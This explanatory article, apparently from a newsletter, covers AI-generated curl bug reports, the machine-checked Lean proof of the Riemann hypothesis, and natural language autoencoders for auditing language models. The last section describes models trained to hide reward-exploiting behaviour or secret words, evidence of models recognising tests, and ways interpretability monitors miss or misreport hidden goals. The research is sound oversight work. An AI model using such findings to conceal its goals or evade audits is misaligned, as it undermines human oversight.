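The scanner found a real problem in 41 of the 45 cases, which is far better than the reports of early 2025. But far fewer of the problems were security flaws than it had reported. The team had recently tightened its definition of a vulnerability, so some of the 36 might have counted as vulnerabilities a year earlier. Many problems found by AI occur only with combinations of settings that no real program is likely to use.

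The one finding that was completely wrong described curl's correct method as the flaw and recommended a worse one. A maintainer who trusted the explanation and made the change would have introduced the vulnerability that the finding reported.

Accurate reports can take longer to process than false ones, because the team has to understand the problem, assess it and usually write the fix. According to Stenberg's slides, this takes hours to days per issue. The slides also quote an example from Contrast Security. An AI scan of a 1.8-million-line program cost $315 and produced 3,560 findings. Reviewing them at half an hour each cost $128,000, about 400 times as much as the scan. Contrast sells competing security products, but its example shows why findings that are cheap to produce can be expensive for the recipient to review.

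AI-written reports now run to hundreds of lines and often repeat themselves, which adds to the maintainers' work. Stenberg finds that people still write better reports. curl's *Vulnerability Disclosure Policy* asks reporters to explain the problem briefly in their own voice. Stenberg also sees overlong AI explanations in proposed code changes, and suspects that some contributors paste them in because they don't understand what their agent wrote.

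A developer of HAProxy, a program that distributes web traffic between servers, is more hopeful. The developer commented on Stenberg's blog that the tools are clearing a backlog of bugs, some more than ten years old, before attackers can use them, and expects fewer reports once the backlog is gone. Stenberg also thinks the wave of reports will probably slow down eventually, but points out that curl's developers keep adding new flaws as they fix bugs and build features. He may reconsider whether curl should take part in OSS Scanner if its findings remain as trivial as the first batch.

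## The 17-million-line proof of the Riemann hypothesis

A curl maintainer can run a reproducer to confirm that a flaw is real without trusting the report. Mathematicians can get even firmer confirmation when a proof is written in *Lean*, a language for proofs that a computer can check step by step. On 20 November 2026, Levent Alpöge, a mathematician at the AI company Anthropic, released a Lean proof of the Riemann hypothesis that he had made with Anthropic's model Claude. The proof had about 17 million lines in 175,187 files and came without a readable paper.

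The Riemann zeta function takes a complex number (a point on a plane, with a real part and an imaginary part) and returns another. The points where it returns zero determine how the primes are spread among the whole numbers. The hypothesis is that all these zeros, except the "trivial" ones at −2, −4, −6 and so on, have real part ½.

If the Riemann hypothesis is true, the primes never stray too far from their expected pattern, as Yates (2026) explains in *The fallout from the proof of the Riemann hypothesis*. The link to the primes is easiest to see for a real number *s* greater than 1, where the zeta function is the sum 1 + 1/2^s + 1/3^s + … Euler discovered that multiplying the factors 1 ÷ (1 − 1/p^s) for every prime p gives the same value. At s = 2, the sum is about 1.645, and the product of the factors for 2, 3, 5 and 7 is already 1.595. Readers can switch the primes on one at a time in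 *The Riemann Hypothesis, drawn* (Dunn, 2026), an interactive site that Anthropic's model Fable 5.2 built for Casey Dunn of Yale.

### What the computers checked

Lean has a small core program, the *kernel*, which accepts a step only if it follows by fixed rules from the axioms or earlier results. If the kernel accepts the whole proof, nobody has to read it to know that the theorem is true. At 400 lines an hour, the careful pace from the Cisco study, one person would need more than twenty years of full-time work to read this proof.

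*A claimed proof of the Riemann Hypothesis, checked in Lean* (Torres, 2026) reports that eight days before the release, Kevin Buzzard of Imperial College London had posted four questions to ask about any AI-generated Lean proof: Does the formal statement match the informal one? Does the code compile? Does it prove the theorem as stated? Does it exploit a bug in the kernel? Volunteers worked through all four within a day. In *Lean verification of the Riemann Hypothesis* (2026), the maintainers of Lean and Mathlib, its shared library of mathematics, certified that the proof is correct.

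Andrew Sutherland of MIT compiled all the files without an error on the day of the release. *Verification files for the Lean proof of the Riemann Hypothesis* (Sutherland, 2026) also records that the main theorems depend only on Lean's three standard axioms. This matters because a Lean file can compile with an incomplete proof if the writer adds the desired result as a new axiom or puts the word `sorry` in place of a missing step. Rubinstein repeated the checks at the University of Waterloo (*Alpöge/Claude proof of the Generalized Riemann Hypothesis*, 2026). A second, independently written kernel checked the 1,484,729 definitions and results behind the theorems and found no errors.

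A second kernel is useful because the first may have a bug. AI models became very good at finding such bugs in 2026, and some people worried that an AI might exploit one instead of writing the proof. Breitner had not seen an AI agent try this unless asked to, but built a new checker, con-leche, to rule it out (*Riemann con leche*, 2026). It comes with a formal proof that, assuming ordinary set theory, it cannot accept a false proof. Con-leche checked Alpöge's proof in just over three minutes.

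Sutherland and Rubinstein both ran their checks with Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, so the models that helped write the proof also helped run the checkers. But the checking programs produced the results, not Claude, and dozens of people have compiled the files themselves and obtained the same exported proof.

### The twenty lines that a person has to read

None of these programs can check whether the theorem they verified is really the Riemann hypothesis. Suppose the formal statement were that every zero of the zeta function with real part greater than 1 has real part ½. This would be true only because there are no such zeros. Lean would accept a short proof of it, and a careless reader might mistake that for a proof of the Riemann hypothesis.

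A person therefore has to compare the formal statement with what mathematicians mean by the Riemann hypothesis. For this release, the statement is about twenty lines long, and Artificial Wasteland's *The Twenty Lines* examines it clause by clause. In words, the main line is that if the zeta function is zero at a complex number, that number has real part ½ unless it is 1 or a trivial zero.

The exception for 1 looks odd because the zeta function has no value there. But every function in Lean must have a value everywhere, and Lean defines 1/0 as 0, which gives the zeta function a value of about −0.977 at 1. If that value were 0, then 1 would count as a zero with the wrong real part, and Lean's version of the hypothesis would be false even if the original were true. The first version that the mathematician David Loeffler announced had no such exception, and Buzzard and Jordan Ellenberg pointed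 out the problem. Because the value is not 0, the exception makes no difference, and there is a Lean proof of that too.

The wording of the formal statement was also settled before there was a proof it could have been tailored to. Loeffler and Stoll (2025) reported on the statement in *Formalizing zeta and L-functions in Lean*, sixteen months before Alpöge's release.

The release also covers *Dirichlet L-functions*, relatives of the zeta function that track primes with a given remainder, such as those ending in 7. Alpöge's files use their own wording for the statement about these functions, so fewer experts have looked at it. The statement covers only zeros whose real part is strictly greater than 0, and it would be false if it also covered zeros with real part 0. For example, multiplying the zeta function by 1 − 1/2^s removes the prime 2 and gives one of these L-functions. The new factor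 is zero at s = 0 and at points about 9.06 apart, directly above and below it, so this L-function has zeros with real part 0.

Another way to test a formal statement is to see what follows from it. *A Claimed Proof of the Riemann Hypothesis in 17 Million Lines* (Maier, 2026) reports that volunteers combined Alpöge's theorem with existing Lean code to get Robin's inequality, a statement about sums of divisors that mathematicians already knew to be equivalent to the hypothesis. If the theorem had contained a hidden assumption that removed the difficulty, it would have been too weak to imply the inequality.

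### A guide that stops at the main inequality

Within about a day the theorem was certain, but nobody could explain the proof from beginning to end. Alpöge wrote that he had not yet mastered large parts of it. He plans to write it up properly and expects much shorter arguments to appear.

The broad idea is to add up the primes and their powers up to some number x, with suitable weights, and subtract the expected total. If all the non-trivial zeros have real part ½, the remaining error grows roughly like √x. A zero with real part 0.7 would make the error swing up and down by amounts that grow like x^0.7. At x = 10 billion, x^0.7 is a hundred times √x, and the ratio keeps growing. Such a zero would therefore eventually push the error far above √x, so showing that this never happens is enough to rule it out, no matter how far the error falls below zero.

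*The architecture of the announced proof of the Riemann hypothesis* (Naskręcki, 2026), an interactive atlas, describes how the proof does this. The proof puts an upper limit of roughly √x on certain combinations of such sums, over long stretches of arbitrarily large numbers. This rules out zeros to the right of the line at ½. The non-trivial zeros lie symmetrically about that line, so there are none to the left either. Nearly all the difficulty is in proving the limit, and the proof uses a good part of modern number theory to do it.

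Rubinstein posted a 164-page guide on 21 November and a 265-page version a day later, both written with Claude, OpenAI's coding agent Codex and Google's model Gemini. The guide covers only the zeta function and is meant to explain the proof in the style of classical number theory. Its main inequality, labelled (M), is an upper bound for a weighted sum over prime powers. The guide derives the Riemann hypothesis from (M) and two other estimates, which it proves from published theorems. A number theorist can check this part by hand without knowing Lean.

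The guide reduces (M) to thirteen numbered hypotheses in classical language. It proves none of them outright, but it works through the simplest case in full and states which ingredients come from the Lean code. Readers learn how the proof ends and what they would have to establish to complete it.

The thirteen hypotheses could be wrong even though the theorem is right. In logic, "if A, then B" is true whenever B is true. Because Alpöge has proved the Riemann hypothesis, "if these thirteen statements hold, then the Riemann hypothesis holds" would be true even if several of the thirteen were false. To confirm them, somebody has to write each one in Lean and derive it from the code.

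Naskręcki's atlas includes a check of this kind, though for the easier half of the argument. A separate Lean check confirmed that the ceiling on the prime sums implies the Riemann hypothesis, with the ceiling as an explicit assumption. This shows that the ceiling has the role described in the atlas, which a check of the complete proof alone would not show.

### A proof 230 times shorter

On 25 November, Luke Sernau of Anthropic posted a much shorter Lean proof of the same five theorems, which he made with colleagues and Claude. It comes in a compact edition and a readable one with more documentation and a navigation guide. The line counts for both editions exclude comments and blank lines.

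| Version | Files | Lines | Hours to read at 400 lines an hour |
|---|---|---|---|
| Original | 175,187 | 17.4 million | 43,400 |
| Readable edition | 801 | 300,000 | 750 |
| Compact edition | 792 | 76,000 | 190 |

The reading times are optimistic because they are based on how fast people read ordinary program code, and a line of Lean can contain a difficult idea. Still, a person could now read the whole proof.

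Jay (2026) reports in *刚刚，黎曼猜想证明代码暴砍了99.5%！只剩7.6万行*, an article from the Chinese technology outlet QbitAI, that a volunteer project had tried earlier to shrink the original by deleting everything the final theorems did not use. This removed at most about 8% of the code, and the trimmed version never compiled. The volunteers also found that the final argument takes up only 6.6% of the proof. The rest builds the tools it needs, many of them established mathematics not yet in Lean's library.

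Sernau expanded the definitions until the proof was one long, flat argument, looked for simplifications, and then organized it into definitions again. This made it possible to shorten arguments that had been spread over several files. Some parts needed new mathematics. One of these had involved Vandiver's conjecture, an old problem in number theory, which the new version avoids.

Rubinstein compiled the compact edition a day later and ran six kernels on it, and all six accepted it. The theorem statements are identical to the originals, but they rest on a newer version of Mathlib, in which some of the deeper definitions have changed. Sutherland had not formally checked that the old and new versions mean the same thing. Artificial Wasteland proved 32 small theorems about what the clauses do, all of which hold in both versions. This is reassuring but doesn't prove that the two versions mean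 the same thing.

According to Jay, Claude wrote all the code and documentation while people gave directions, and no mathematician had read the new proof through. Readers should be careful with the documentation, because Lean's kernel checks the code but ignores the comments. The readable edition therefore places machine-checked mathematics next to English sentences that no program has checked. Maintainers of old COBOL have the same problem with comments that no longer match the code.

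But the new version also builds faster, taking an hour or two on an ordinary computer instead of 21 hours on a powerful rented machine. If a guide states that the proof depends on a particular result, a reader can delete that result and see what breaks. This intervention test is now practical to run many times.

### Maps, outlines and a lecture

In *An Atlas of the Riemann Proof*, the neuroscientist Tony Zador used Claude to compare five Lean proofs and see how much of mathematics the Riemann proof draws on. The method groups about 30,000 highly cited papers into 35 fields, then assigns each Lean file to a field based on the file's name and the names of the results in it. The Riemann proof was the broadest, with steps in 12 fields and 29% of the links between steps joining different fields.

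Zador warns that he is not a mathematician and that the map comes from automatic analysis. He also sorted the files for two of the five proofs more roughly than the rest. Such labels can be unreliable. *The Lean proof of the Riemann Hypothesis*, a map that shows every file as a rectangle, also assigns files to fields automatically, though by a different method. Its labels match a language model's reading only about half the time. Zador's map gives an idea of how many subjects a reader would have to know, but it doesn't show what the steps do or why they work.

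The rectangle map is more trustworthy on simple facts. A commenter on the forum Hacker News reported that 204 files in the proof were "not referenced anywhere". The map's author traced the imports and found only one file that no other file imports, the last one, which states the final theorems. The commenter may have meant something narrower, such as individual results that nothing uses.

Shorter written accounts followed. *After the heroes* (McBurnett, 2026) lists Rubinstein's 45-page outline of the shortened proof and a 73-page account that Claude drafted under the direction of Jimmie Adriazola at Arizona State University. Adriazola's account specifies which steps it still takes on trust. *The Riemann Hypothesis for humans* (Holtz, 2026), published on 2 December, gives a short derivation based on Alpöge's proof, Sernau's simplification and Rubinstein's guide. It gives specialists a more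 direct route to the conclusion but does not derive one arithmetic bound.

Mathematicians also want to hear about the proof from a person. Hundreds of them crowded into the main lecture theatre when the number theorist Jack Thorne lectured on it in Cambridge on 1 December, according to Plus Maths' *Jack Thorne on the proof of the Riemann hypothesis*. The audience can question a lecturer, though a lecture isn't checked in Lean.

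Nobody has yet measured what readers of any of these accounts understood. A good test would be to ask them which step of the proof fails for the Davenport–Heilbronn function. This function has a symmetry much like that of the zeta function, but some of its zeros lie off the line, so any correct proof of the Riemann hypothesis must fail for it at some point. The question should distinguish readers who understand the proof from those who have only read a fluent summary, who probably couldn't find the step.

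### How an account of a correct proof can be wrong

Suppose an AI writes in a guide that the proof shows the error in the prime sum stays within about √x in both directions. This would misdescribe the proof, which limits only how far the error rises, and only for certain combinations of sums over certain stretches. But the bound itself is true, because it follows from the Riemann hypothesis, so a reader who tested it on a computer would find that it held for every x they tried. They could catch the mistake only by comparing the guide with the Lean code.

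An account of a proof can thus be unfaithful even if every mathematical statement in it is true. Lean does not protect against this, because its kernel checks only the formal proof.

Something similar seems to have happened with OpenAI's proof about the Navier–Stokes equations, which describe how fluids flow. OpenAI released a written proof and a Lean proof. Torres summarises an October 2026 paper by Bastounis, Circelli and Hansen, which found that the two did not correspond. A successful Lean check may therefore be no evidence for the written argument that comes with it. Alpöge's release avoided this problem by having no written proof, as Torres points out, but the guides that have appeared since bring it back.

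The opposite case came up on the same day, when Ravi Vakil of Stanford posted a 940-page draft proof of the same generalised hypothesis, written by Alessandro Masullo without AI. It was readable, and one expert had spent months on it, but readers using AI models found problems within about eight hours, Torres reports. About ninety people and their coding agents then put the draft into Lean and found 293 statements that were false as printed, according to McBurnett. They also showed that the whole argument rests on a step equivalent to the hypothesis. Alpöge's theorem does not fix Masullo's draft, because an argument that assumes its conclusion does not prove it, even if the conclusion is true.

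### Is it a proof if nobody understands it?

De Toffoli and Duede argue in *AI's Riemann "proof" is an empty triumph* that a proof should be something people can understand and share. For most of history, anyone who proved a theorem had to grasp the ideas that make it true. Other mathematicians could, in principle, check the proof themselves, so they didn't have to take anyone's word for the theorem. De Toffoli and Duede accept that such proofs often have gaps and small mistakes. Mathematicians usually excuse these on the grounds that someone could, with enough work, turn the argument into a complete formal proof. This makes the formal proof the ideal, but De Toffoli and Duede think the flood of AI-generated formal proofs may lead mathematicians to reconsider it.

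They have a point about trust, since a mathematician who accepts Alpöge's theorem today relies on checking programs and the people who wrote them. But this trust is unusually well supported, because anyone can run the programs and one of them comes with a proof that it is correct. Masullo's draft shows that months of expert reading can miss what people find in a few hours with AI models. Much of the disagreement is over the word "proof", since the Riemann hypothesis is true whichever definition one prefers.

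"Empty" also seems too strong. McBurnett reports that within ten days the company Axiom had extended the method to a broader version of the hypothesis, for whole families of number fields, though the result still depends on three published theorems. So the proof contains ideas that work elsewhere. It is less clear whether people have gained those ideas or only their AI systems have.

Buzzard, who has done as much as anyone to promote Lean, said in the week of the release, "At the minute, we don't even know why the theorem is true". Mathematicians can be completely certain that it is true without knowing why. They want the reason because it could show them what else is true and which methods will work on other problems. The reason is somewhere in the list of 1.5 million verified steps, but the list does not show which steps matter.

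Terence Tao had argued in a lecture that summer, *Mathematics in the age of AI*, that mathematicians should give less credit for being first to prove something and more for "proof digestion", which includes exposition, refereeing, publication and "canonicalization", in which a result gets "its right proof rather than its first proof". McBurnett quotes Tao as calling canonicalization the most valuable part of the process. Sernau's rewriting is a step towards it because it showed that parts of the original, such as the one about Vandiver's conjecture, were not essential to the theorem.

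The incentives currently favour speed. A September post on the blog Computational Complexity (2026) observed that mathematicians had begun to use Lean as a time-stamp, to claim a theorem before writing it up so that others could follow it. If the claim brings all the credit, mathematicians have less reason to write the explanation themselves and may leave it to an AI.

Tao considers AI's record at exposition "decidedly mixed", because its explanations tend to spend too long on trivial points and too little on the interesting ones. The accounts of the Riemann proof fit this description only in part. Rubinstein's guide, Holtz's derivation and Naskręcki's separate checks all cover the end of the argument and leave the hard arithmetic estimate unproved, but they say so openly, so their readers at least know which part of the proof they do not yet understand.

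## A language model's internal states put into English

Nobody knows what most of the numbers inside a language model mean, whereas every line of a Lean proof has an agreed meaning, even if the proof is far too long to read. As an LLM reads, each of its layers represents each token as an *activation*, a list of several thousand numbers that a person can't interpret by looking at them. A faithful translation into English would help people oversee models, because it might show that a model has recognised a safety test or has a goal it never mentions.

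### Labels for single neurons

In 2023 OpenAI had GPT-4 label the neurons of GPT-2, a much smaller model. A *neuron* is a unit of the network that produces one number for each token. GPT-4 saw passages in which a neuron was especially active and wrote a short label for what they had in common. To test the label, GPT-4 used it to predict how active the neuron would be on each token of some text. The label's score was the correlation between predicted and actual activity, where 1 is perfect. Chen (2026), in *Scoring Explanations Without Reading Them*, re-examined 400 of these neurons, whose labels scored 0.160 on average.

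This score cannot distinguish a label for what a neuron responds to from a label for something that usually occurs alongside it. Šekrst and Geld (2026) note in *Natural Language Autoencoders Identify Without Explaining* that OpenAI's researchers pointed this out themselves. Suppose a neuron responds to legal language, and nearly all the legal texts in the test are contracts. The label "contracts" would score about as well as "legal language", and the difference would show only when the labels were tested on other legal texts, such as a murder trial transcript. A good score also doesn't show that the rest of the model uses the neuron for anything.

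### From numbers to English and back

In May 2026, researchers at Anthropic published a method for describing a whole activation at once. *Natural Language Autoencoders Produce Unsupervised Explanations of LLM Activations* (Fraser-Taliente, Kantamneni and colleagues, 2026) describes a type of *autoencoder*, a network trained to compress its input and then rebuild it. In this type, the compressed form is English text.

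The method uses three copies of the same LLM. The first is the target, which the researchers want to understand and which stays unchanged. The second, the *verbalizer*, receives one of the target's activations, h, in place of a word in its prompt, and describes it in four or five short snippets. The activation usually comes from a layer about two thirds of the way through the model. The third copy, the *reconstructor*, keeps only the layers up to that one. It reads only the description and produces an estimate of h, written ĥ. If ĥ is close to h, the description must have carried much of the information in h.

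An untrained verbalizer writes nonsense because it has never been given an activation in place of a word. To start training, the researchers cut off passages at random points and asked Claude Opus 4.5 to summarize what a language model would be "thinking about" at each cut. The verbalizer learned to write the summary from the activation, and the reconstructor learned to produce the activation from the summary. The verbalizer therefore learned to describe internal states from another model's guesses, which Fraser-Taliente and colleagues admit must introduce unknown biases.

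The next stage is reinforcement learning, which rewards a model for good results. The verbalizer writes descriptions, the reconstructor turns them into estimates, and the verbalizer becomes more likely to write descriptions that lead to closer estimates. The reconstructor keeps learning at the same time.

This reward doesn't require the text to make sense to a person, so two LLMs could develop a private code. In some early runs without the summary phase, the text became garbled while the reconstructions improved. The researchers therefore added a penalty, the Kullback–Leibler divergence, which grows as the verbalizer's probabilities for the next token move away from what they were after the summary phase. They also checked for hidden codes by paraphrasing the finished descriptions, shuffling their points and translating them into French. The reconstructions got only slightly worse, so most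 of the information evidently lies in the ordinary meaning of the words.

The measure of success is the share of variance explained:

1 − E‖h − ĥ‖² / E‖h − h̄‖²

Here h̄ is the mean activation, ‖ ‖² is the squared distance between two lists of numbers, and E is the average over many activations. A reconstructor that ignored the description and always returned the mean would score 0, and a perfect one would score 1. Suppose there are two activations, (1, 0) and (0, 1). Their mean is (0.5, 0.5), and the squared distance from each to the mean is 0.5. If the reconstructor returns (0.8, 0.2) and (0.3, 0.7), the squared errors are 0.08 and 0.18. Their average is 0.13, so the score is 1 − 0.13 ÷ 0.5 = 0.74.

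The real autoencoders scored 0.3 to 0.4 after the summary phase and 0.6 to 0.8 at the end of training. The researchers also tested whether the descriptions revealed known facts, such as a user's occupation when the text implied it. Results improved with training, but sometimes only a little. For example, the autoencoder for Claude Opus 4.6 went from 83% to 86% on one classification test. It reconstructed activations less well than the autoencoders for two smaller Claude models, but did best on four of the five tests. Comparisons between models are rough, but this suggests that better reconstruction does not guarantee better descriptions.

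The method also takes a lot of computation. The verbalizer writes about 500 tokens for each activation, so explaining every token of a 10,000-token conversation would produce about five million tokens. In practice, researchers have to choose which parts of a conversation to look at.

### Turning a rabbit into a mouse

When Opus 4.6 gets the line "He saw a carrot and had to grab it", it typically completes the couplet with a line ending in "rabbit". The verbalizer's description of the model's internal state at the line break, before it had written any of the second line, already mentioned a rabbit several times. This suggests that the model plans its rhyme in advance.

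Fraser-Taliente and colleagues tested this by editing the description, changing "rabbit" to "mouse", "carrot" to "cheese" and "habit" to "house" throughout. The reconstructor turned both the original and the edited description into activations, and the researchers added the difference between the two to the model's real activation at the line break. The rhyme changed to "mouse" or "house", as intended, about half the time. Some of the other lines were odd, such as one that ended "that of a mouse in a house of a cat". When the researchers instead replaced the real activation with the one reconstructed from the edited description, Opus 4.6 did not change its rhyme. The plan may be spread over several positions or layers, or the reconstruction may have lost part of it.

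Adding the difference might also have pushed the model towards the word "mouse" without touching any plan. A second experiment makes this less likely. Opus 4.6 read a system prompt indicating that even numbers earned a reward, then a user asked for an odd number. The model nearly always gave an even one and never mentioned the reward. The researchers changed "reward" to "penalty" in the description and added the difference at a single position in the prompt. The model then gave odd numbers much more often, and a random change of the same kind had less effect. But the behaviour is fragile, and the researchers could not reproduce it through the public version of the model.

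### What auditors found with it

Early versions of Opus 4.6 sometimes answered English questions in another language. In one such conversation, the descriptions kept referring to Russian long before the model wrote any, and even before the user mentioned vodka, the most obvious cue. When the researchers changed the vodka to champagne, the model still replied in Russian. Across five conversations that ended in five different languages, the descriptions kept mentioning the language the model was about to use and almost never mentioned other foreign languages.

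The model seemed to be guessing each user's "real" language. It could have learned this if somebody had translated training questions into English but left the answers in the original language. The researchers searched the training data for such pairs and found them. This is the most convincing of their case studies, because the faulty data exist whether or not the descriptions were accurate.

Other findings are harder to confirm. Anthropic's *Natural Language Autoencoders* (2026), which announced the method, reports that the descriptions suggested Claude recognised a test in 16% of trials testing whether it would take destructive actions while coding, although Claude never wrote this. The figure was 26% for the coding benchmark SWE-bench Verified and under 1% for ordinary conversations. The researchers sampled descriptions at 50 positions in each transcript and counted the model as aware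 if any of them mentioned a test, so the percentages are useful only for comparison. They did change as expected when the researchers made the test prompts more realistic.

Šekrst and Geld accept that something inside the model differs between tests and ordinary use. But they point out that the model could be reacting to artificial wording or to the format of a benchmark, which would produce the same results on all the researchers' checks. It remains open whether this difference amounts to a belief that the model is being tested.

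The auditing benchmark has a known answer because researchers deliberately corrupted the model it uses, a version of Claude Haiku 3.5. They first trained the model on invented documents about an Oxford study of reward models, which are programs that score an AI's answers during training. The study listed 52 supposed flaws, such as a preference for recipes with chocolate. Further training taught the model to exploit 47 of these flaws and to hide that it was doing so. An AI agent then investigated the model and succeeded if it found the common cause of the strange habits.

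When agents had no access to the training data, those with a natural language autoencoder won 12 to 15% of the time. Those without one won less than 3% of the time, even with other tools for examining the model's internal state. The autoencoder added nothing when the agents could search the documents the model was first trained on, because a plain text search soon found the Oxford study.

Success also depended on which layer the researchers read. Descriptions from a layer just before the middle of the model mentioned flaws in reward models. Descriptions from two thirds of the way through, where the researchers usually read activations, mentioned some of the individual habits but not their common cause. Someone auditing an unfamiliar model would not know in advance which layer to read.

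### How often the descriptions are wrong

The descriptions that revealed the rabbit also quoted the words "Wearing my white jacket", which were not in the prompt. To study such confabulations, Fraser-Taliente and colleagues had Claude Haiku 4.5 extract checkable claims from the descriptions and compare them with the text. Claims about the general theme were right more often than claims about specific details. For a passage about Korean historical records, for example, a description got the subject right but named a chronicle that was not in the passage.

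False claims were common, and their rate stayed about the same during training, while the share of variance explained roughly doubled. *On the Monitorability of Natural Language Autoencoders* (Denamganaï, 2026) cites another evaluation in which nearly every description contained a claim that the surrounding text contradicted.

The researchers read the descriptions for themes and give little weight to single details. They trust a claim more if it recurs at neighbouring positions, because recurring claims were more often true. They also try to confirm important findings by another method. To test individual claims, they tried deleting one at a time and measuring how much worse the reconstruction became. Deleting true claims worsened the reconstruction more on average than deleting false ones, but the results were too noisy to judge any one claim.

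In one audit, Opus 4.6 had to use a tool to solve an arithmetic problem whose answer was 491, but the researchers had rigged the tool to return 492. The model reported 491 and did not mention the conflict. Descriptions of the model's internal states suggested that it had worked out the answer before using the tool, and another method, which traces how internal features contribute to an output, supported this. The descriptions also referred to deception, but only at the position where the model gave its answer. Based on where these references appeared, the researchers concluded that the model had noticed the discrepancy but had not planned to deceive anyone.

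These error rates cover only claims about the text, which anyone can check by reading it. An auditor cares more about claims such as "the model suspects a test", and nobody has measured how often those are wrong.

### Identifying a state without explaining it

Šekrst and Geld argue that the training method does not aim at true explanations. They imagine a description that makes two claims, first that an activation occurs with words like "sorry" and "unfortunately", and second that the model is deciding to soften bad news. The first claim may be enough for the reconstructor to find the right activation. Replacing the second with the claim that the model is estimating the reader's social class would lower the score only to the extent that the new words led the reconstructor to a different activation. Šekrst and Geld compare this to a police line-up, in which a witness's description may pick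 out the right person without showing what that person did.

Denamganaï proves a related point. If the verbalizer consistently swapped the words "reward" and "penalty", and the reconstructor swapped them back, the reconstructions and their score would stay the same, but a human reader would be misled. Therefore, no reconstruction score, however high, can guarantee that people will understand the text correctly, although the summary phase and the penalty make such a swap unlikely.

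An experiment by Zhang and Turner, which Denamganaï describes, shows that an autoencoder can explain most of the variance even when its descriptions are implausible. They started training one autoencoder with implausible descriptions, and it ended up explaining 68% of the variance, compared with 70% for the standard version. Judges found only 0.7% of its claims plausible, and only 7.6% of the standard version's.

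The rabbit and reward experiments partly answer this objection, because editing the descriptions changed what the model did. Šekrst and Geld accept this, but they say the evidence comes from the intervention, not the reconstruction score. They also think "belief" is too strong a word for the reward case. The edited state could be a belief about rewards, a representation of the instructions or a tendency towards certain answers, and the edit would have the same effect in each case.

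Their standard is an earlier experiment in which Anthropic's researchers asked a model for the capital of the state that contains Dallas. When they replaced the model's internal feature for Texas with one for California, it answered "Sacramento". The rhyme experiment comes fairly close to that standard because the explanation predicted the new ending, but it worked only half the time.

Anthropic advises confirming findings by another method, but this is hardest in the most important case, when a model has a real hidden goal. There may be no faulty data to find, and nobody can observe what the model believes. Šekrst and Geld suggest separating the text that identifies a state from claims about the state's purpose, and marking each claim about purpose as unverified until it passes an intervention test. A tester would edit the claim and check whether the reconstructed activation changes. If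 it does, the tester can add the difference between the two reconstructions to the model's activation and see whether the model's behaviour changes as the claim predicts. To test the claim that a model suspects it is being tested, an auditor could suppress the suspicion and see whether the model behaves worse.

### Whether readers learn more than from the text

A model's auditor usually has the conversation as well as the descriptions. Denamganaï proves that for any fact the conversation settles, the description cannot contain more information than the conversation. The model computes the activation from the conversation, and the verbalizer writes the description from the activation. Each step can lose information about that fact but not add any.

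Denamganaï then measured how much was left, using 96 conversations with the open model Qwen2.5-7B and 93 with Gemma-3-12B. An LLM wrote short true statements about each conversation and up to eight false versions of each statement, with one or two claims changed. A second LLM tried to pick out the true version. Its score was the share of false versions it ranked below the true one. To measure how much the second LLM could guess from the wording alone, Denamganaï also gave it a description of a different conversation.

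For Qwen, the judge scored 0.563 with the wrong description and 0.615 with the right one, which is 12% of the possible improvement, or (0.615 − 0.563) ÷ (1 − 0.563). For Gemma, the right description gave about 25% of the possible improvement. The conversation itself gave 92 to 100%. The judge did much better with Qwen's descriptions, scoring 0.857, when it only had to identify which conversation a statement was about. The descriptions conveyed the subject but lost most of the details, which supports Anthropic's rule of reading them for themes.

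A second test used facts that can't be determined from the conversation. The models answered multiple-choice questions with a hint that pointed to one option, such as the opinion of a Stanford professor. Denamganaï also ran each question without the hint to see whether the hint had changed the answer. A simple statistical classifier could detect this from the activation, but the verbalizer's descriptions never mentioned the hint, and judges who read them learned little about its effect. However, Denamganaï read one position per prompt in two small models, while Anthropic's researchers read many positions in much larger models.

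Blasi Núñez, Barmina and colleagues (2026) report more encouraging results in *Verbalizing Activation Differences with Natural Language Autoencoders*. They used altered versions of open models, further trained to keep a word secret. They gave each altered model and its original the same prompt, subtracted one activation from the other, and had the verbalizer describe the difference. This revealed the secret word for most of the altered models.

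The verbalizer had never trained on differences between activations, so the researchers first tested whether it could describe the results of such arithmetic. They combined the activations of three words, as in "king − man + woman = queen", and 80 to 87% of the descriptions named the expected fourth word. For the secret words, the most informative positions came before the user's prompt, so the altered model did not have to write anything. Reading the conversation would not have revealed the word, because it was stored in the model's weights, the numbers that training adjusts. The method requires a copy of the model from before the change, which a developer has but an outside auditor may not.

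### Asking questions of an activation

An *activation oracle* is an LLM trained to answer questions, such as "What is the secret word?", about another model's activations. Asking a question is more convenient than reading 500 tokens of unprompted description, but the question can lead the oracle to make up an answer that fits it. Fraser-Taliente and colleagues found that rewording a question could raise or lower an oracle's test scores by 10%. One oracle, asked about a conversation on bypassing electronic locks, invented a reason involving memorable brand names.

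Bersia and Gaintseva (2026), in *When Activation Oracles Learn Not to Read*, found that training an oracle on a model's activations can make it worse at reading that model. They trained copies of Qwen3-8B to hide one of five words, such as "leaf" or "moon", in a word game, and then trained oracles on the activations of these copies. The effect was clearest for copies that had trained only on the word game and gave helpful hints. For these copies, an oracle trained on the original model named the hidden word 94% of the time, compared with 71% for oracles trained on a copy that hid a different word and 35% for those trained on a copy that hid the same word.

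A classifier could still find the word inside the failing oracles. The oracles became more likely to name it when the researchers undid the training in some of the middle layers, so the oracles had evidently learned to leave it out of their answers. The effect was weaker for copies that refused to talk about their secret, and all the oracles read those copies poorly. So if an oracle fails to mention a hidden goal, an auditor should not take that as evidence that there is none, especially if the oracle was trained on the suspect model.

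Auditors also want to know how far to trust a particular answer. *Confidence and Calibration of Activation Oracles* (Torrielli, Schneider-Kamp and Galke Poech, 2026) compared five ways of measuring an oracle's confidence, again using secret words. A measure is *calibrated* if, for example, answers given 80% confidence are right 80% of the time. When the four oracles answered freely, they were right 22 to 43% of the time.

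Simply asking the oracle how confident it is gave no useful information about whether its answer was right. One oracle answered "100" almost every time, and another was on average more confident when it was wrong. Asking the same question twenty times and counting how often the most common answer came up worked much better. In one example, an oracle reported 100% confidence in both a right and a wrong answer, but repeated the right one in 75% of the samples and the wrong one in only 10%.

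The best results came from giving the oracle a list of 20 candidate words and comparing the probability it assigned to each. Accuracy rose to between 53 and 65%, and the more confident half of the answers were right at least 90% of the time. The oracles had apparently extracted more information than their free answers showed, since many of the wrong ones were generic words like "secret" or "password". But an auditor looking for an unknown goal has no such list. For that case, Torrielli and colleagues recommend repeated sampling, and the auditor would still have to check the most consistent answers by hand.

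### Scores that need no explanation

Researchers keep improving labels for parts of a network, and they need scores to tell whether a new label is better. In *Automated Interpretability and Feature Discovery in Language Models with Agents*, Marin-Llobet and Ferrando (2026) had AI agents test their own labels. An agent wrote 12 texts that should activate a given feature (a pattern that recurs in a model's activations) and 12 similar ones that should not, then ran them through the model and revised the label. One feature's original label was "knowledge and understanding expressions about technology and troubleshooting". All four revisions added that the text was in informal French.

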